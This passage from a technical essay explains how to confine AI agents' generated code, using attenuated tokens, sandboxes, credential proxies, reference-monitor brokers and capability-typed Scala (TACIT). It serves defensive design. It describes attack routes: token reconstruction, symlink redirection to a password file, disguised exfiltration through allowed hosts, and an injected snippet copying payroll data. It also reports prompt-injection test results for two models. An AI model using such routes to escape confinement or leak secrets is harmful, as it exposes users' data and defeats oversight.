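s2 = MAC(s1, "path = /project/sales.csv")
s3 = MAC(s2, "operation = read")
s4 = MAC(s3, "time < 14:10")
```

The script receives the identifier, all four caveats as plain text, and s4. When it sends a request, the service does the following:

1. It uses the identifier to find K.
2. It computes s0 to s4 again from K and the caveats in the token.
3. It compares its result with the signature that the script sent.
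4. It checks every caveat against the request.

A request to read the file at 14:05 succeeds. A request to write to it fails because of the `read` caveat, and a request to read it at 14:12 fails because of the time limit.

The script can add its own caveat, for example to give a helper program only three minutes, because it has s4 and can use it as the next key. Adding "time < 15:00" would not extend its access, since the earlier limit still applies. To remove the ten-minute limit, the script would have to present s3, which it cannot compute from s4. Removing or editing an earlier caveat would change every later signature, and the script does not have the keys to recompute them. Birgisson and colleagues give a short security argument, and López-Alt (2013) studies the constructions formally in *Cryptographic Security of Macaroon Authorization Credentials*.

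The hashes keep the caveats intact, but the service still has to interpret them correctly. Birgisson and colleagues consider a read-only storage service that later adds a `delete` operation. Because reading was once the only operation, old tokens may not mention operations at all, so they might now permit deletion. The assistant's folder token has this weakness, but the script's token does not, because it names the one operation it allows. Birgisson and colleagues suggest that the service refuse new operations to old tokens.

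### When the script can read its parent's token

The narrowing is useless if the script can find s1. The script's own token contains the identifier and the folder caveat as plain text, so the script can combine them with s1 to rebuild the assistant's token. It could then read or change anything in the project folder, and the service would accept its requests because the rebuilt token is genuine.

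A script can easily gain access to the original, broader token by accident, and Hegelich and colleagues list keys inherited through environment variables among the common weaknesses of coding agents. The harness must therefore create the narrower token in a process that the script cannot inspect, and start the script in a clean environment. A stricter design keeps all credentials outside the sandbox.

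Dantuluri and Sundi (2026), in *Delegation Without Trust*, simulated 2,000 random delegations in an environment with 8,100 possible actions. A compromised sub-agent could perform all 8,100 if it held its parent's broad token, but an average of 1.5 if it held a narrowed one. The size of the gap comes from how they set up the simulation, but it illustrates what a script would gain by finding the parent's token.

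### Public keys and central issuers

Only someone with the root key can check a macaroon, and anyone with that key can also make new ones. A storage service and a database run by different companies could not safely share a root key, because each could then forge macaroons that the other would accept.

Public-key signatures solve this, because one key makes the signature and a different key checks it. In Biscuit, a token format, the issuer signs a first block of permissions and each holder can append a signed block of restrictions. *Vouchsafe* (2026) describes how these rules are expressed in a small logic language that a service can evaluate locally. UCAN, by Zelenka, Holmgren and colleagues, uses a chain of certificates, each passing authority to the holder of a particular key. A UCAN delegation names a subject, a command and a policy. For example, it might permit creating blog posts only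 with the status "draft".

Birgisson and colleagues preferred keyed hashes largely for speed. On their server, a keyed hash took 2.8 microseconds, compared with 458 for an RSA signature. The difference matters much less for agents, because running the model takes far longer than either operation. When Prakash timed an orchestrator delegating a job to a specialist, the protocol accounted for about 2.4 milliseconds of the 2.7 seconds the delegation took.

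OAuth token exchange, which Jones, Nadalin and colleagues set out in *RFC 8693*, instead relies on a central server. The assistant sends the server its token and requests a new one for the script. The server can apply its latest policy and refuse. But the standard does not guarantee that the new token will be narrower. Muruaga points out that a server can follow the standard and record a chain of delegations without reducing the authority at each step, so whether the subset rule holds depends on how the operator configures the server.

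| | Macaroon | Biscuit | UCAN | OAuth token exchange |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Can the holder narrow it offline? | Yes | Yes | Yes | No |
| Who can check it? | Anyone with the secret root key | Anyone with the issuer's public key | Anyone with the public keys in the chain | Services that trust the central server |
| Is a stolen copy usable? | Yes, unless a caveat prevents it | Yes, unless a restriction prevents it | Not without the recipient's private key | Yes, unless the server ties it to a key |
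| Does it show who delegated? | No | Only if the delegators add this | Yes | Optionally |

*Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025) recommends token exchange for centrally managed systems, and Biscuit or macaroons for looser networks. A harness that narrows a token for every short script can avoid a network request each time by doing so offline.

Revocation is slow when tokens are used offline, because a service that checks them without contacting anyone cannot detect a recent cancellation. In UCAN, an earlier delegator can issue a signed revocation, but it takes effect only when it reaches the service. The specification treats revocation as a last resort, preferring expiry, and Prakash's protocol likewise recommends tokens that last under an hour. A macaroon can carry a caveat that requires fresh proof from another service, such as one that tracks revocations, but the holder must be online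 to get it. A central issuer can stop issuing tokens at once, but those already issued may work until they expire unless the service checks with the issuer.

An issuer can limit theft by tying a token to a private key, so that a thief would need both. This helps if the token leaks through a log, but not if the script can also use the key. Dantuluri and Sundi confirmed this limitation when they tested their own system, which accepted a stolen token from an attacker who could also present the victim's identity.

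Signatures are better audit evidence than keyed hashes. In *Comparing capability systems*, a discussion started by Karp (2026), Mark Miller explained that the recipient of a message protected by a shared key can tell who sent it but cannot prove this to anyone else. Macaroons have this weakness because the service has the root key and could have written every caveat itself.

The token exchange standard has an optional field, `act`, that can list the earlier parties in a chain, so Prakash's criticism that token exchange leaves no record of the original chain is too strong. The weakness is that services cannot rely on this field. Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues (2026), in *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, note that the standard has no common rules for preserving and checking the list over several exchanges.

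### Should the owner have a say?

With macaroons, Biscuit and UCAN, anyone who holds a token can pass on part of its authority without asking. The holder is usually the only one who knows how it will divide up its work. In *Subjects, Not Authors*, Lee and Lee (2026) argue that this isn't enough when the data belong to someone else. They study dataspaces, networks in which organisations share data under contracts that software enforces. A company may be willing to let its partner's agent read its data, but not to let that agent pass the access on to sub-agents the company doesn't know.

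They propose that the owner set a ceiling C on what any sub-agent may receive. The holder can still narrow the grant however it likes, but the child must satisfy

P(child) ⊆ P(parent) ∩ C

Their example is a certificate of origin, a trade document. The main agent may read public facts, such as the country of origin, and commercial figures, such as the declared value. It receives the companies' names only in anonymised form. Under the ceiling, sub-agents may read only the public facts, may use them only for customs clearance, and may not delegate further. A sub-agent may therefore check the product's tariff code but not look up the buyer's name.

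The declared value shows the effect of the ceiling better than the lookup does. The main agent may read the value, so under free delegation it could pass on that access, but the ceiling forbids this. In the lookup, the main agent cannot see the names either, so the ordinary subset rule would already block the request.

In this design, a sub-agent presents a chain of signatures that leads back to its organisation, and the data owner's server looks up what the contract allows. The sub-agent carries no permissions itself, so every action has to wait for the server. Revocation is also coarser than with tokens, because cancelling the contract cuts off every agent at once, and removing a single sub-agent requires an amendment.

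Lee and Lee acknowledge that the main agent could still read the declared value and paste it into the sub-agent's prompt. The ceiling limits only what the sub-agent can request directly, and makes those requests easier to audit. This helps an owner who worries about careless delegation, but does little for one who expects the partner's agent to leak data.

Prakash's protocol combines the two positions. Whoever issues the first token sets the maximum number of handovers, three by default, and holders are otherwise free to delegate. An ordinary bearer token could not enforce this limit, because a holder can always share an exact copy.

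### Which agent systems use such tokens?

The most common agent frameworks did not narrow tokens in 2026. Dantuluri and Sundi ran LangGraph, inspected the code of CrewAI and AutoGen, and found that none of the three had built-in limits on delegation. They also read the July 2026 authorisation rules of the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting agents to tools. Those rules tie each token to one server but don't narrow it when one agent delegates to another. Dantuluri and Sundi work for a company that sells access control for agents, but anyone can check their findings against the public code and specifications.

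Several research systems do narrow tokens, and their developers have tested them:

- Prakash's protocol builds on Biscuit. It rejected all 100 attempts to widen a grant and all 600 attacks in a separate test. Ordinary signed tokens also stopped four of the six kinds of attack, including widening. The other two broke rules specific to the protocol, its limit on handovers and its requirement to state a purpose.
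- Dantuluri and Sundi's broker issues a new, narrower token at each handover and checks every tool call. It withstood 11 attacks on its design and rejected 200,000 forged tokens. They have not released the code.
- Hegelich and colleagues' harness uses tokens modelled on macaroons. Its security layer blocked 93.9% of attacks before they adjusted it to the test cases, and it blocked none of the harmless calls. That layer also filters paths, programs and network addresses, so the result does not isolate the effect of the tokens.

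Muruaga's system follows the same subset rule but stores each agent's scope on a trusted server instead of in a token. Muruaga tested it on 99 delegation chains of two to eight steps. In all four cases the developers tested their own systems, mostly with attacks they chose. The results are good evidence that the code enforces its rules, but weaker evidence of how well it would resist an attacker looking for other ways in.

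Other proposals are still designs. Lee and Lee tested other parts of their system but not the ceiling. *AgentKernel* (Zou, Guo and colleagues, 2026) proposes chains of capabilities as part of an operating system for agents and supports the design with analysis. Prakash notes that Google DeepMind's proposal for macaroon-based delegation tokens also came without an implementation.

Standards are also at an early stage. *Verifiable Attenuated Delegation for AI Agent Chains* (Asor, 2026) and *An Attenuated Delegation Profile for Automated Agents* (Hassan, 2026) are draft internet standards under which a service checks every step of the chain. Karp belongs to a Decentralized Identity Foundation group that is writing another specification for delegation between agents. The group has decided to use capabilities, and in March 2026 Karp expected it to choose signed certificates.

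## What can generated code reach from a sandbox?

A narrowed token limits what a remote service will do for the sales script, but not what the script can do on the machine where it runs. Suppose the harness starts the script in a fresh virtual machine (a simulated computer with its own operating system) and copies in all the assistant's environment variables so that nothing breaks. One of them holds the mail token. If the virtual machine has a network connection, the script can use that token to send mail as the user without escaping the virtual machine.

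*Security boundaries in agentic architectures* (Ubl and Arora, 2026) reports that most agents run generated code with full access to the agent's secrets. A common first fix is to put the harness and the generated code in one sandbox. This protects the company's other systems, but the code can still steal the harness's credentials because they are in the same sandbox. Ubl and Arora recommend running the harness and the generated code on separate machines. They published the article for Vercel, which sells such sandboxes, but the reasoning applies to any vendor's.

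### Adding resources or blocking them

Saltzer and Schroeder's advice to start from no access also applies to sandboxes. Cloudflare's *Project Think* (2026) argues for it because developers then have to decide what the code should be able to do instead of guessing everything it shouldn't be able to do.

If the harness starts from full access and blocks specific things, generated code can reach everything else on the machine. If the harness starts from no access, the code can reach only what it is granted. When someone saves a new password file, the code can therefore read it under the first approach unless someone also updates the list of what's blocked. Under the second, the code can't read the file unless someone grants access to it.

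According to Anthropic's documentation, a shell command run in Claude Code's optional sandbox can by default read the entire computer except certain denied directories, and no built-in list protects credential files. For network access, the sandbox instead uses a list of permitted internet domains, which starts empty.

### Capsicum

Capsicum, part of the FreeBSD operating system, can take away a program's access to every file except those it already has open. Access to those open files would be enough for the `cat` command described earlier. In *Capsicum*, Watson, Anderson and colleagues (2010) extended Unix instead of replacing it, and adapted several FreeBSD utilities and Google's Chromium browser to use the new features.

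A process refers to each open file or network connection by a number called a file descriptor. Capsicum can limit a file descriptor to specific rights, such as reading without writing. It also has a capability mode, in which a process can no longer open files by their ordinary paths or use other system-wide names. A process that enters this mode can never leave it, and neither can any process it starts.

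For the sales chart, the harness starts a small launcher, which does the following:

```
sales = open("sales.csv", read)
chart = open("chart.png", write)
limit_rights(sales, {read})
limit_rights(chart, {write})
enter_capability_mode()
run(script, sales, chart)
```

The launcher uses its ordinary access to open the two files, then gives up that access before any generated code runs. The script can then read one file and write to the other. It cannot open the customer list, even if it has the exact path.

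Capability mode doesn't close anything that is already open. If the launcher inherited a database connection from the assistant, the script can send queries over it, so the launcher has to close every descriptor the script doesn't need. The launcher must also load the plotting library beforehand or pass a descriptor for a folder that contains it, because Python normally finds the library by path.

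### WebAssembly

WebAssembly is a compact instruction format that programs in many languages can compile to. A WebAssembly program, called a module, can calculate and use its own block of memory, but it has no instruction for opening a file or contacting another computer. To do either, it has to call an import, which is a function that its host supplied when loading it. If the host supplies no imports, the module can only calculate and return a result.

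WebAssembly therefore meets Miller's requirement of loader isolation, but an import that runs any shell command would undo the whole arrangement.

Many modules use a standard set of imports called WASI, which covers files, clocks and printed output. Its file functions work only inside folders that the host has opened for the module. For the sales chart, the harness copies the CSV file into an empty folder called `job` and runs the compiled script with Wasmtime, a program that executes WebAssembly:

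```
wasmtime run --dir job::/work chart.wasm
```

The module finds the folder under the name `/work` and cannot name the project folder or the user's other files. The harness supplies a copy because this command lets the module write to the folder as well as read it, and a faulty script can then damage only the copy. When the script finishes, the harness moves the chart to its proper place.

Wasmtime can also stop a module after a fixed number of instructions. This limit handles endless loops more predictably than a time limit, which may cut off a working script on a busy computer.

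The main drawback is that the script and all its libraries have to compile to WebAssembly, so a Python plotting library with parts written in C needs a special build. WebAssembly also enforces these limits only when the code runs, whereas some programming languages can reject a forbidden action at compile time.

### JavaScript isolates with bindings

An isolate is a separate instance of V8, the engine that runs JavaScript in Google's Chrome browser. Cloudflare has long run its customers' code in isolates, and in March 2026 it opened a beta of Dynamic Workers, which lets one program start another in a new isolate with code supplied at runtime. Varda, Pai and Gupta report in *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* that an isolate starts in a few milliseconds and uses a few megabytes of memory. A harness can therefore create an isolate for a single script and then discard it, instead of reusing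 a sandbox that still holds files from an earlier task.

The code in the isolate reaches outside resources through bindings, objects the harness chooses to pass in. Cloudflare's *Bindings* gives the example of an agent that may post to one chat room. The harness defines a class with a `post` method and passes the isolate a stub, a reference that sends each method call back to the harness. The harness keeps the room's name and the secret key.

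The same pattern works for the sales chart if the project folder is in cloud storage. In simplified form:

```
class SalesFile extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  read() { return storage.get(this.ctx.props.path) }
}
class ChartFile extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  write(image) { return storage.put(this.ctx.props.path, image) }
}

env.LOADER.load({
  mainModule: "script.js",
  modules: { "script.js": generated_code },
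  env: {
    SALES: ctx.exports.SalesFile({ props: { path: "sales.csv" } }),
    CHART: ctx.exports.ChartFile({ props: { path: "chart.png" } })
  },
  globalOutbound: null
})
```

The script can call `SALES.read()` and `CHART.write(image)`. It cannot change either path, because the harness fixed both when it created the stubs. Ubl and Arora recommend the same precaution for tools in general. An agent helping one customer should get a tool tied to that customer's data, because injected text could alter a customer number that the agent passes as an argument.

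These stubs are object capabilities that work across a sandbox boundary. According to Cloudflare's documentation, code cannot forge a stub and can obtain one only by receiving it. `SalesFile` serves the same purpose as the read-only wrapper in the earlier example, and whoever writes it must be just as careful about what each method returns.

The last line of the call, `globalOutbound: null`, cuts off the network. Cloudflare's *Egress control* describes blocking the internet and then adding specific bindings as the most secure design. But if the developer leaves that line out, the isolate inherits its parent's network access, usually the whole public internet, according to the reference pages in Cloudflare's *Dynamic Workers*. Forgetting the line therefore gives the script far too much access, unlike forgetting a binding, which gives it too little.

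A harness can instead let the script make web requests and filter them. Varda and colleagues support this for scripts that use existing web libraries, but they consider it harder to get right than a wrapper. The filter has to interpret every request that an existing service might accept, including any headers and parameters that could change its meaning, whereas a wrapper's author only writes the functions the script should have.

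Isolates suit JavaScript best. Cloudflare also supports Python, but warns that it is much slower to start and recommends JavaScript for one-off generated code.

### Containers and small virtual machines

Scripts that need ordinary Python, shell commands or compiled libraries usually run in a container. A container has its own view of the file system, the running processes and the network, but it shares the host's kernel, the core of the operating system. The harness controls which host folders are mounted (made available inside the container) and which network addresses the container can reach.

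Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* includes a sample command for a locked-down container. Adapted to the sales chart, it could look like this:

```
docker run --rm \
  --network none --read-only --tmpfs /tmp \
  --cap-drop ALL --security-opt no-new-privileges \
  --user 1000:1000 --memory 2g --pids-limit 100 \
  -v /project/sales.csv:/in/sales.csv:ro \
  -v /jobs/17/script.py:/in/script.py:ro \
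  -v /jobs/17/out:/out \
  plot-image python /in/script.py
```

The three `-v` lines grant file access. They mount the CSV file and the script as read-only (`ro`) and an empty output folder as writable. `--network none` blocks outside connections, and the limits on memory and processes stop a runaway script from using up the machine's resources. `plot-image` contains Python and the plotting library but no user data.

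Changing the first mount to `-v /project:/in:ro` would remove much of this protection, because the script could then read the whole project, including any file that holds the database password. Anthropic warns that even read-only access to a code folder can expose credentials and suggests copying only the files the agent needs.

A script can't detect a file that isn't mounted in its sandbox. Apache Magpie's *Secure agent setup*, which documents an Apache project's configuration for Claude Code, describes the same effect with bubblewrap, a Linux sandboxing tool. A command that tries to read a cloud password file gets "No such file or directory" instead of "Permission denied". On macOS, the Seatbelt sandbox leaves the file in place and refuses the operation.

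The harness can put a stronger barrier between the script and the kernel without changing the grant. gVisor handles most of a container's system calls (requests to the kernel) in a separate program. According to Anthropic, it adds almost no time to pure calculation but can make work that opens and closes many files 10 to 200 times slower. A virtual machine runs its own kernel. Firecracker can start a small virtual machine in under 125 milliseconds with less than 5 MiB of extra memory. All isolation layers have had security flaws, and Varda and colleagues acknowledge that these are more common in V8 than in typical software for running virtual machines.

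In the sales chart example, any of the four mechanisms can keep the script away from the mail token. Which one to use depends mostly on the script's language, how quickly it has to start and how much the operator trusts the barrier. With all four, the harness still has to set which resources the script can reach.

### Keeping secrets outside

Some scripts have to use a service that requires a credential. Suppose the next chart needs exchange rates from a paid web service. The harness could place the service's token in the sandbox, but the script could then print it, save it or send it elsewhere. A credential proxy avoids this by holding the secret outside:

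1. The harness gives the proxy the real token and the address of the exchange-rate service.
2. The script sends its request without a token.
3. The proxy intercepts the request and checks the destination.
4. If the destination matches, the proxy adds the token and forwards the request.
5. The script receives the exchange rates but never the token.

Ubl and Arora write that the proxy stops generated code from copying the secret and using it elsewhere later, but "doesn't prevent misuse during active runtime". If the token also permits changes to the account, a script might be able to change the billing address through the proxy. The harness therefore still needs a token with narrow permissions, or a proxy that accepts only certain requests, such as reading today's rates.

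A proxy that checks only a request's destination gives the script a kind of ambient authority. The request carries the user's authority to the address the script names because of where the script is running. If two scripts share a proxy, the proxy must also identify which one sent each request, or it could become a confused deputy and use one script's credential for the other.

Most web traffic is encrypted from the sender to the service, so an ordinary proxy can see the destination but cannot add anything to the request. The operator can let the proxy decrypt and re-encrypt the traffic, but programs in the sandbox must then trust the proxy's certificate. Alternatively, the harness can offer a tool, such as `get_rates(date)`, that makes the authenticated request from outside the sandbox. This avoids intercepting encrypted traffic, and the tool can permit much less than the token does.

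Claude Code has a version of the proxy for its sandboxed commands. The user can mask a credential so that commands receive only a placeholder, which the proxy replaces with the real value on requests to chosen hosts. If the user names no hosts for that credential, the proxy makes the replacement for every domain on the allowlist, which could send a code-hosting token to an unrelated service.

### What coding tools put in the sandbox

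A coding tool that advertises a sandbox may apply it to only some of its parts. Claude Code's documentation from October 2026 describes a sandbox that is off by default. Once the user turns it on, different limits apply to different parts of the tool:

| Part of Claude Code | What limits it |
|---|---|
| Shell commands and the processes they start | The operating system's sandbox |
| Built-in tools for reading, editing and fetching web pages | Permission rules |
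| Local tool servers, and hooks (commands that run automatically at set moments) | Neither; they run with the user's full access |

Claude Code applies permission rules before an action starts, based on the text of the request. The operating system enforces the sandbox while the command runs, so the sandbox still limits a command that does more than its name suggests. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* makes the same distinction. Once an approved command has started another program, the coding tool can no longer monitor or control that program, but the operating system can.

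If Claude Code runs the sales script as a sandboxed command with the default settings, the script can read nearly every file the user can read and change most of the project folder. It has no network access until a domain is approved. The sandbox does limit the script, but it still allows more access than the job needs, which is one input file and one output file.

The user can narrow what sandboxed commands can read by blocking the home directory and then permitting the project. Blocking a file in the sandbox does not stop Claude Code's own file-reading tool, so the user also needs a matching permission rule. Apache Magpie's configuration uses both. It also runs GitHub's command-line program outside the sandbox, so that the program can use its stored token but sandboxed commands cannot read the token. That program is then a deputy with broad authority, and Apache Magpie relies on confirmation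 prompts to control it.

Several other settings determine how firm the boundary is:

- If a required component is missing, Claude Code by default runs commands without a sandbox. A setting called `failIfUnavailable` makes it stop instead.
- If a command fails in the sandbox, Claude may ask to run it again outside. Depending on the mode, a person, a classifier model or an existing rule approves the request, and one mode needs no approval. The user can switch these retries off.
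- Sandboxed commands cannot change the files from which Claude Code loads its own settings, because a command that could edit them might grant itself more access.

Claude Code's rules for combining settings follow the downstream rule in one respect. Any settings file, including one from a downloaded project, can deny access to a credential, because this only narrows access. No other settings file can remove that denial. Masking a credential authorises the proxy to send the real value somewhere, so Claude Code accepts masking instructions only from the user or an administrator.

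Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* advises against relying on the command sandbox alone for fully unattended work. The user can instead run all of Claude Code inside a container, a virtual machine or Anthropic's separate sandbox program, so that the isolation also covers the file tools, tool servers and hooks. But this puts the harness and the generated code in the same sandbox, an arrangement Ubl and Arora criticised. Running the command sandbox inside the container adds a second boundary around the commands, and a proxy can keep credentials outside both.

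NVIDIA reports that many other agent systems also sandbox only command-line tools, and recommends enforcing the limits on everything the agent does. Ubl and Arora report that few people use the sandboxes in the coding tools Claude Code and Cursor on desktop computers, because sandboxing can cause compatibility problems.

### Approving a name or approving a file

Permission rules and approval prompts usually refer to files by name, but a name can lead to a different file than the user expects. A symbolic link, for example, is an entry in a folder that points to another file. Suppose the assistant asks to read `style.txt` for the chart's colours, and the user agrees because the name looks harmless. If `style.txt` is a link to the file that holds the database password, the assistant receives the password. The link can also change after the approval, so checking it once is not enough.

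Capsicum and Cloudflare's bindings largely avoid this problem because the script receives an open file or a stub and never looks up a name. The harness still has to open the right file. Coding tools are more exposed to it because the model's requests refer to resources by name throughout a task.

Commey (2026), in *Names Are Not Objects*, traces many recent security failures in coding agents to this gap. The paper presents Zero-Trust Agent Cells (ZTAC), a prototype for macOS that decides on the actual file and then makes sure to use that same file. The agent runs in a sandbox from which it cannot open even its own project files. It has to send every request to a broker, which acts as a reference monitor, a trusted component that checks each relevant action before it takes effect. For a request to read a file, the broker:

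1. checks the agent's signature on the request;
2. follows any links to find the real file, and records the number by which the disk identifies it;
3. applies its rules to the real file's location instead of the requested name;
4. asks a person if the rules require it, showing the real file;
5. opens the file one folder at a time, refusing any links, and stops if the file's number has changed;
6. records the result in a signed log.

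In the example, the prompt would name the password file instead of `style.txt`. Each approval covers one agent, one exact request and one file. It works once and expires after ten minutes. An approval to save changes in Git, which tracks versions of a project, also covers the changes waiting to be saved, so the agent cannot add to them after the review.

The broker starts programs in a sandbox built from the same rules. These programs cannot request approval, so the sandbox blocks any action that would need it.

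Commey tested the design with 74 scripted attacks, including re-creations of 10 publicly reported incidents. The attacker controlled everything on the agent's side, including the model. Commey also tested the design with 46 ordinary operations and 7 longer workflows.

| Configuration | Attacks that succeeded | Attacks held for review | Operations completed | Workflows completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
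| No protection | 74 | 0 | 46 | 7 |
| List of allowed tools and commands | 66 | 0 | 46 | 7 |
| The same list plus a sandbox for commands | 56 | 0 | 46 | 7 |
| ZTAC's broker without the agent's sandbox | 12 | 13 | 43 | 4 |
| Full ZTAC | 2 | 14 | 43 | 4 |

Both attacks that beat the full system sent a secret in disguised form to an address that the rules allowed. Commey presents them as the limit of the design, which controls where data can go but not what the data contain.

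Binding approvals to real files accounts for only a small part of the improvement. When Commey removed that feature alone, 2 more attacks succeeded. Applying the rules to requested names instead of real files let 5 more through, and removing human review let 18 more through. Without the agent's own sandbox, all 10 attacks that bypassed the broker succeeded. The result depends heavily on sending every action through the broker and on people refusing the 14 attacks it held for review. Commey used a simulated reviewer and did not study how often real people would refuse.

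The comparison probably overstates ZTAC's advantage over commercial tools. Commey wrote the attacks largely around the gaps that ZTAC closes, and tested an imitation of current products' command sandboxes instead of the sandboxes themselves. No actual agent took part, and all the tests used one small Python project.

Commey also found eight flaws in ZTAC while building and testing it, seven of which were gaps between a name and the object it referred to. In one, the broker tied an approval to the request but not to the file, so a script could redirect a link to another file after the reviewer had approved the request. Commey fixed all eight, but they show how easily this kind of mistake can remain in a system designed to prevent it.

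The broker added about 4 milliseconds to a request that did no other work, and the 46 operations produced 8 approval prompts. The loss of functions was a bigger drawback. Three workflows failed because ZTAC does not let programs start other programs, protects the files that set up a Python environment, and blocks a common Git shortcut. The ban on starting programs also supports the security argument, because ZTAC writes a file by checking the target and then replacing it in a separate step, which is safe only if nothing changes the folder in between. The broker handles one request at a time and leaves no script running between requests, but it cannot stop the user's own editor from changing the folder between those two steps.

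## Can the programming language enforce the limit?

Suppose the sales script is allowed to read a payroll file and to send requests to the company that hosts its language model. A sandbox that allows both cannot stop the script from sending the salaries to that company, because each step is permitted on its own. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) addresses this problem with TACIT, a system in which an agent writes its actions in the programming language Scala 3. Before the code runs, the compiler checks which resources each part could use and rejects code that could pass classified data to the network or to an ordinary file.

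Existing agents such as Claude Code can connect to TACIT through the Model Context Protocol, so the agent doesn't have to be written in Scala. The agent sends TACIT a snippet of code. If the snippet compiles, TACIT runs it and returns the result. Otherwise the agent receives the compiler's error messages and can try again. The snippet can access files, other programs and the network only through a small library that comes with TACIT.

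### Capabilities recorded in types

A type tells the compiler what kind of value a variable holds, such as text or a number. Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, extends the type with the value's capture set, which lists the capabilities the value can use. These capabilities are object references, as in Miller's model.

If `chart` is a reference to the chart file, a function that takes text could have any of these types:

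| Type | What the function may use |
|---|---|
| `String -> Int` | Nothing except its argument |
| `String ->{chart} Unit` | The chart file |
| `String => Unit` | Any capability |

A function of the first type is pure. (`Unit` means the function returns no useful value.) The compiler works out the capture set from the function's body, so a function that calls `chart.write` gets the set {chart} even if its author wrote no annotation. The set lists everything the function might use, including capabilities it rarely uses.

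A value with a smaller capture set can stand in for one with a larger set, but not the other way round. A pure function can therefore be used anywhere, while a function that uses the chart cannot be used where the program requires a pure one. In effect, the compiler applies the subset rule to every function in the program.

Object capabilities without this tracking control which references a program receives, but they cannot require one function inside the program to use none of them. Odersky and colleagues call this restriction on a single function "local purity", and TACIT relies on it to protect classified data.

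### One snippet that compiles and one that doesn't

The operator of TACIT marks certain folders as classified. When a snippet reads a file from one of them, it receives the text inside a wrapper called `Classified`. In simplified form:

```
trait Classified[T]:
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The `map` method applies a function to the hidden contents and wraps the result. The plain arrow in `T -> U` means that the function must be pure.

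Suppose the user wants to know how many lines the payroll file has. The agent could write:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val payroll = readClassified("/project/secret/payroll.csv")
  val lines = payroll.map(text => text.count(c => c == '\n'))
  println(lines)
}
```

The function passed to `map` uses only its own argument, so its capture set is empty and the compiler accepts the snippet. The result is a wrapped number. TACIT's `println` shows the number in the user's terminal but sends only `Classified(****)` back to the agent. The cloud-hosted model never receives the number, so it cannot repeat it later in the conversation.

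Now suppose an injected instruction persuades the agent to copy the payroll into a file that anyone can read:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val chart = access("/project/chart.txt")
  val payroll = readClassified("/project/secret/payroll.csv")
  payroll.map(text => chart.write(text))
}
```

The compiler handles this snippet as follows:

1. It sees that the function calls `write` on `chart`, so it gives the function the type `String ->{chart} Unit`.
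2. It sees that `map` requires a function of type `String -> Unit`, with an empty capture set.
3. Because {chart} is not a subset of the empty set, it reports an error that names `chart`.
4. No part of the snippet runs, including the lines before the error.

In the experiments, agents wrote code like this, and the compiler rejected it. One snippet tried to print a GitHub key from inside `map`. Another tried to write classified recommendations to a file in the secrets folder. That write might have been harmless, but the compiler rejected it because the capture set records only that the function uses a file, not how sensitive the file's folder is. The agent should have used `writeClassified`, which takes the wrapped text and writes only to classified files.

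### File access that ends with its block

In both snippets, `requestFileSystem` creates a capability for one folder, and the code between the braces can use it. The capability expires at the closing brace. A snippet might try to keep it for longer:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/project") {
  () => access("/project/sales.csv").read()
}
later()
```

The block returns a function that would read the file after the block ends. The compiler rejects the snippet because that function captures the file-system capability, and the type of the block's result may not mention a capability that exists only inside the block. The compiler also rejected an agent's attempt to return a list of open file handles. The block may return the text of an ordinary file, because text carries no capability.

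Unlike a caretaker, TACIT needs no forwarder, because the compiler has already verified that no reference outlives the block. A caretaker is more flexible, though, because its owner can end access at any time.

TACIT still needs some checks at run time. A program can compute a file path from data, so the compiler cannot always know which file it will open. The library checks each path as the program runs and refuses any outside the chosen folder. It also checks web addresses and commands against a list.

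In the published interface, however, the generated code itself specifies the folder, web hosts and commands when it requests access. The types make the code declare what it will use and give up access afterwards, but they do not limit what it can request. An operator who wants such a limit has to build it into the library or run TACIT inside a sandbox.

### Safe mode and the trusted parts

Ordinary Scala lets programmers override the compiler's checks. TACIT compiles all generated code in safe mode, which forbids:

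- unchecked type casts and pattern matches, which could relabel a value as one that holds no capabilities;
- the `caps.unsafe` module and `@unchecked` annotations, which bypass checks;
- reflection, which lets a running program look up and call methods by name;
- global functions and objects that are not themselves safe, including Scala's standard print functions.

Safe mode cannot forbid exceptions, because simple events such as division by zero cause them. An exception's message could reveal a secret, so TACIT catches exceptions and turns them into ordinary values that it can wrap. This makes mistakes harder to notice. In one set of experiments, a function that failed while handling classified data looked successful to the agent, and the user received nothing. The agents' instructions had to include a warning about this.

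The protection depends on the Scala compiler, the TACIT library and the software that runs the compiled code. Library authors can mark a module as safe even if it uses forbidden features internally, for example to store earlier results, and the compiler accepts the label without checking it. There are machine-checked proofs for the type system behind capture checking, but Odersky and colleagues leave a proof for safe mode to future work.

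If an agent needs a language model to summarise classified text, the operator must also trust that model. TACIT can send the wrapped text to a local model and wrap the summary that comes back, but the operator must ensure that the model does not keep the text and use it in later requests. The types also do not guarantee that the summary is accurate. An instruction hidden in a contract could lead the local model to give the user a misleading summary.

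### TACIT's experiments

Odersky and colleagues tested whether secrets could reach the agent's output. They gave agents a sample software project with a folder of API keys, a database and classified documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 injected attacks, the most advanced of which contained ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files. In 11 further trials, the user asked for the secrets directly or pretended to have authority to see them. Each model ran all 131 trials in classified mode, where the secrets were wrapped, and again in unclassified mode, where they were plain text.

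| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Trials without a leak, classified | 100% | 100% |
| Trials without a leak, unclassified | 98.5% | 91.6% |
| Ordinary tasks done correctly, classified | 99.2% | 90.0% |
| Ordinary tasks done correctly, unclassified | 83.3% | 88.3% |

Without the wrapper, Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted every injection but revealed secrets in 2 of the 11 trials with a dishonest or malicious user. MiniMax M2.5 revealed them in 8 of those 11 trials and in 3 of the 120 trials with injections. Both models are older than the strongest ones of December 2026, so these rates are a poor guide to how often a current model would leak secrets without protection, but the protection itself does not depend on the model.

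The design should produce a perfect score in classified mode, so the trials mostly test whether the library has an obvious gap. They are weaker evidence about an attacker who searches for flaws in the compiler. The wrapper probably did not make Claude Sonnet 4.6 better at its tasks. In unclassified mode, the model often ran out of time or turns, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing.

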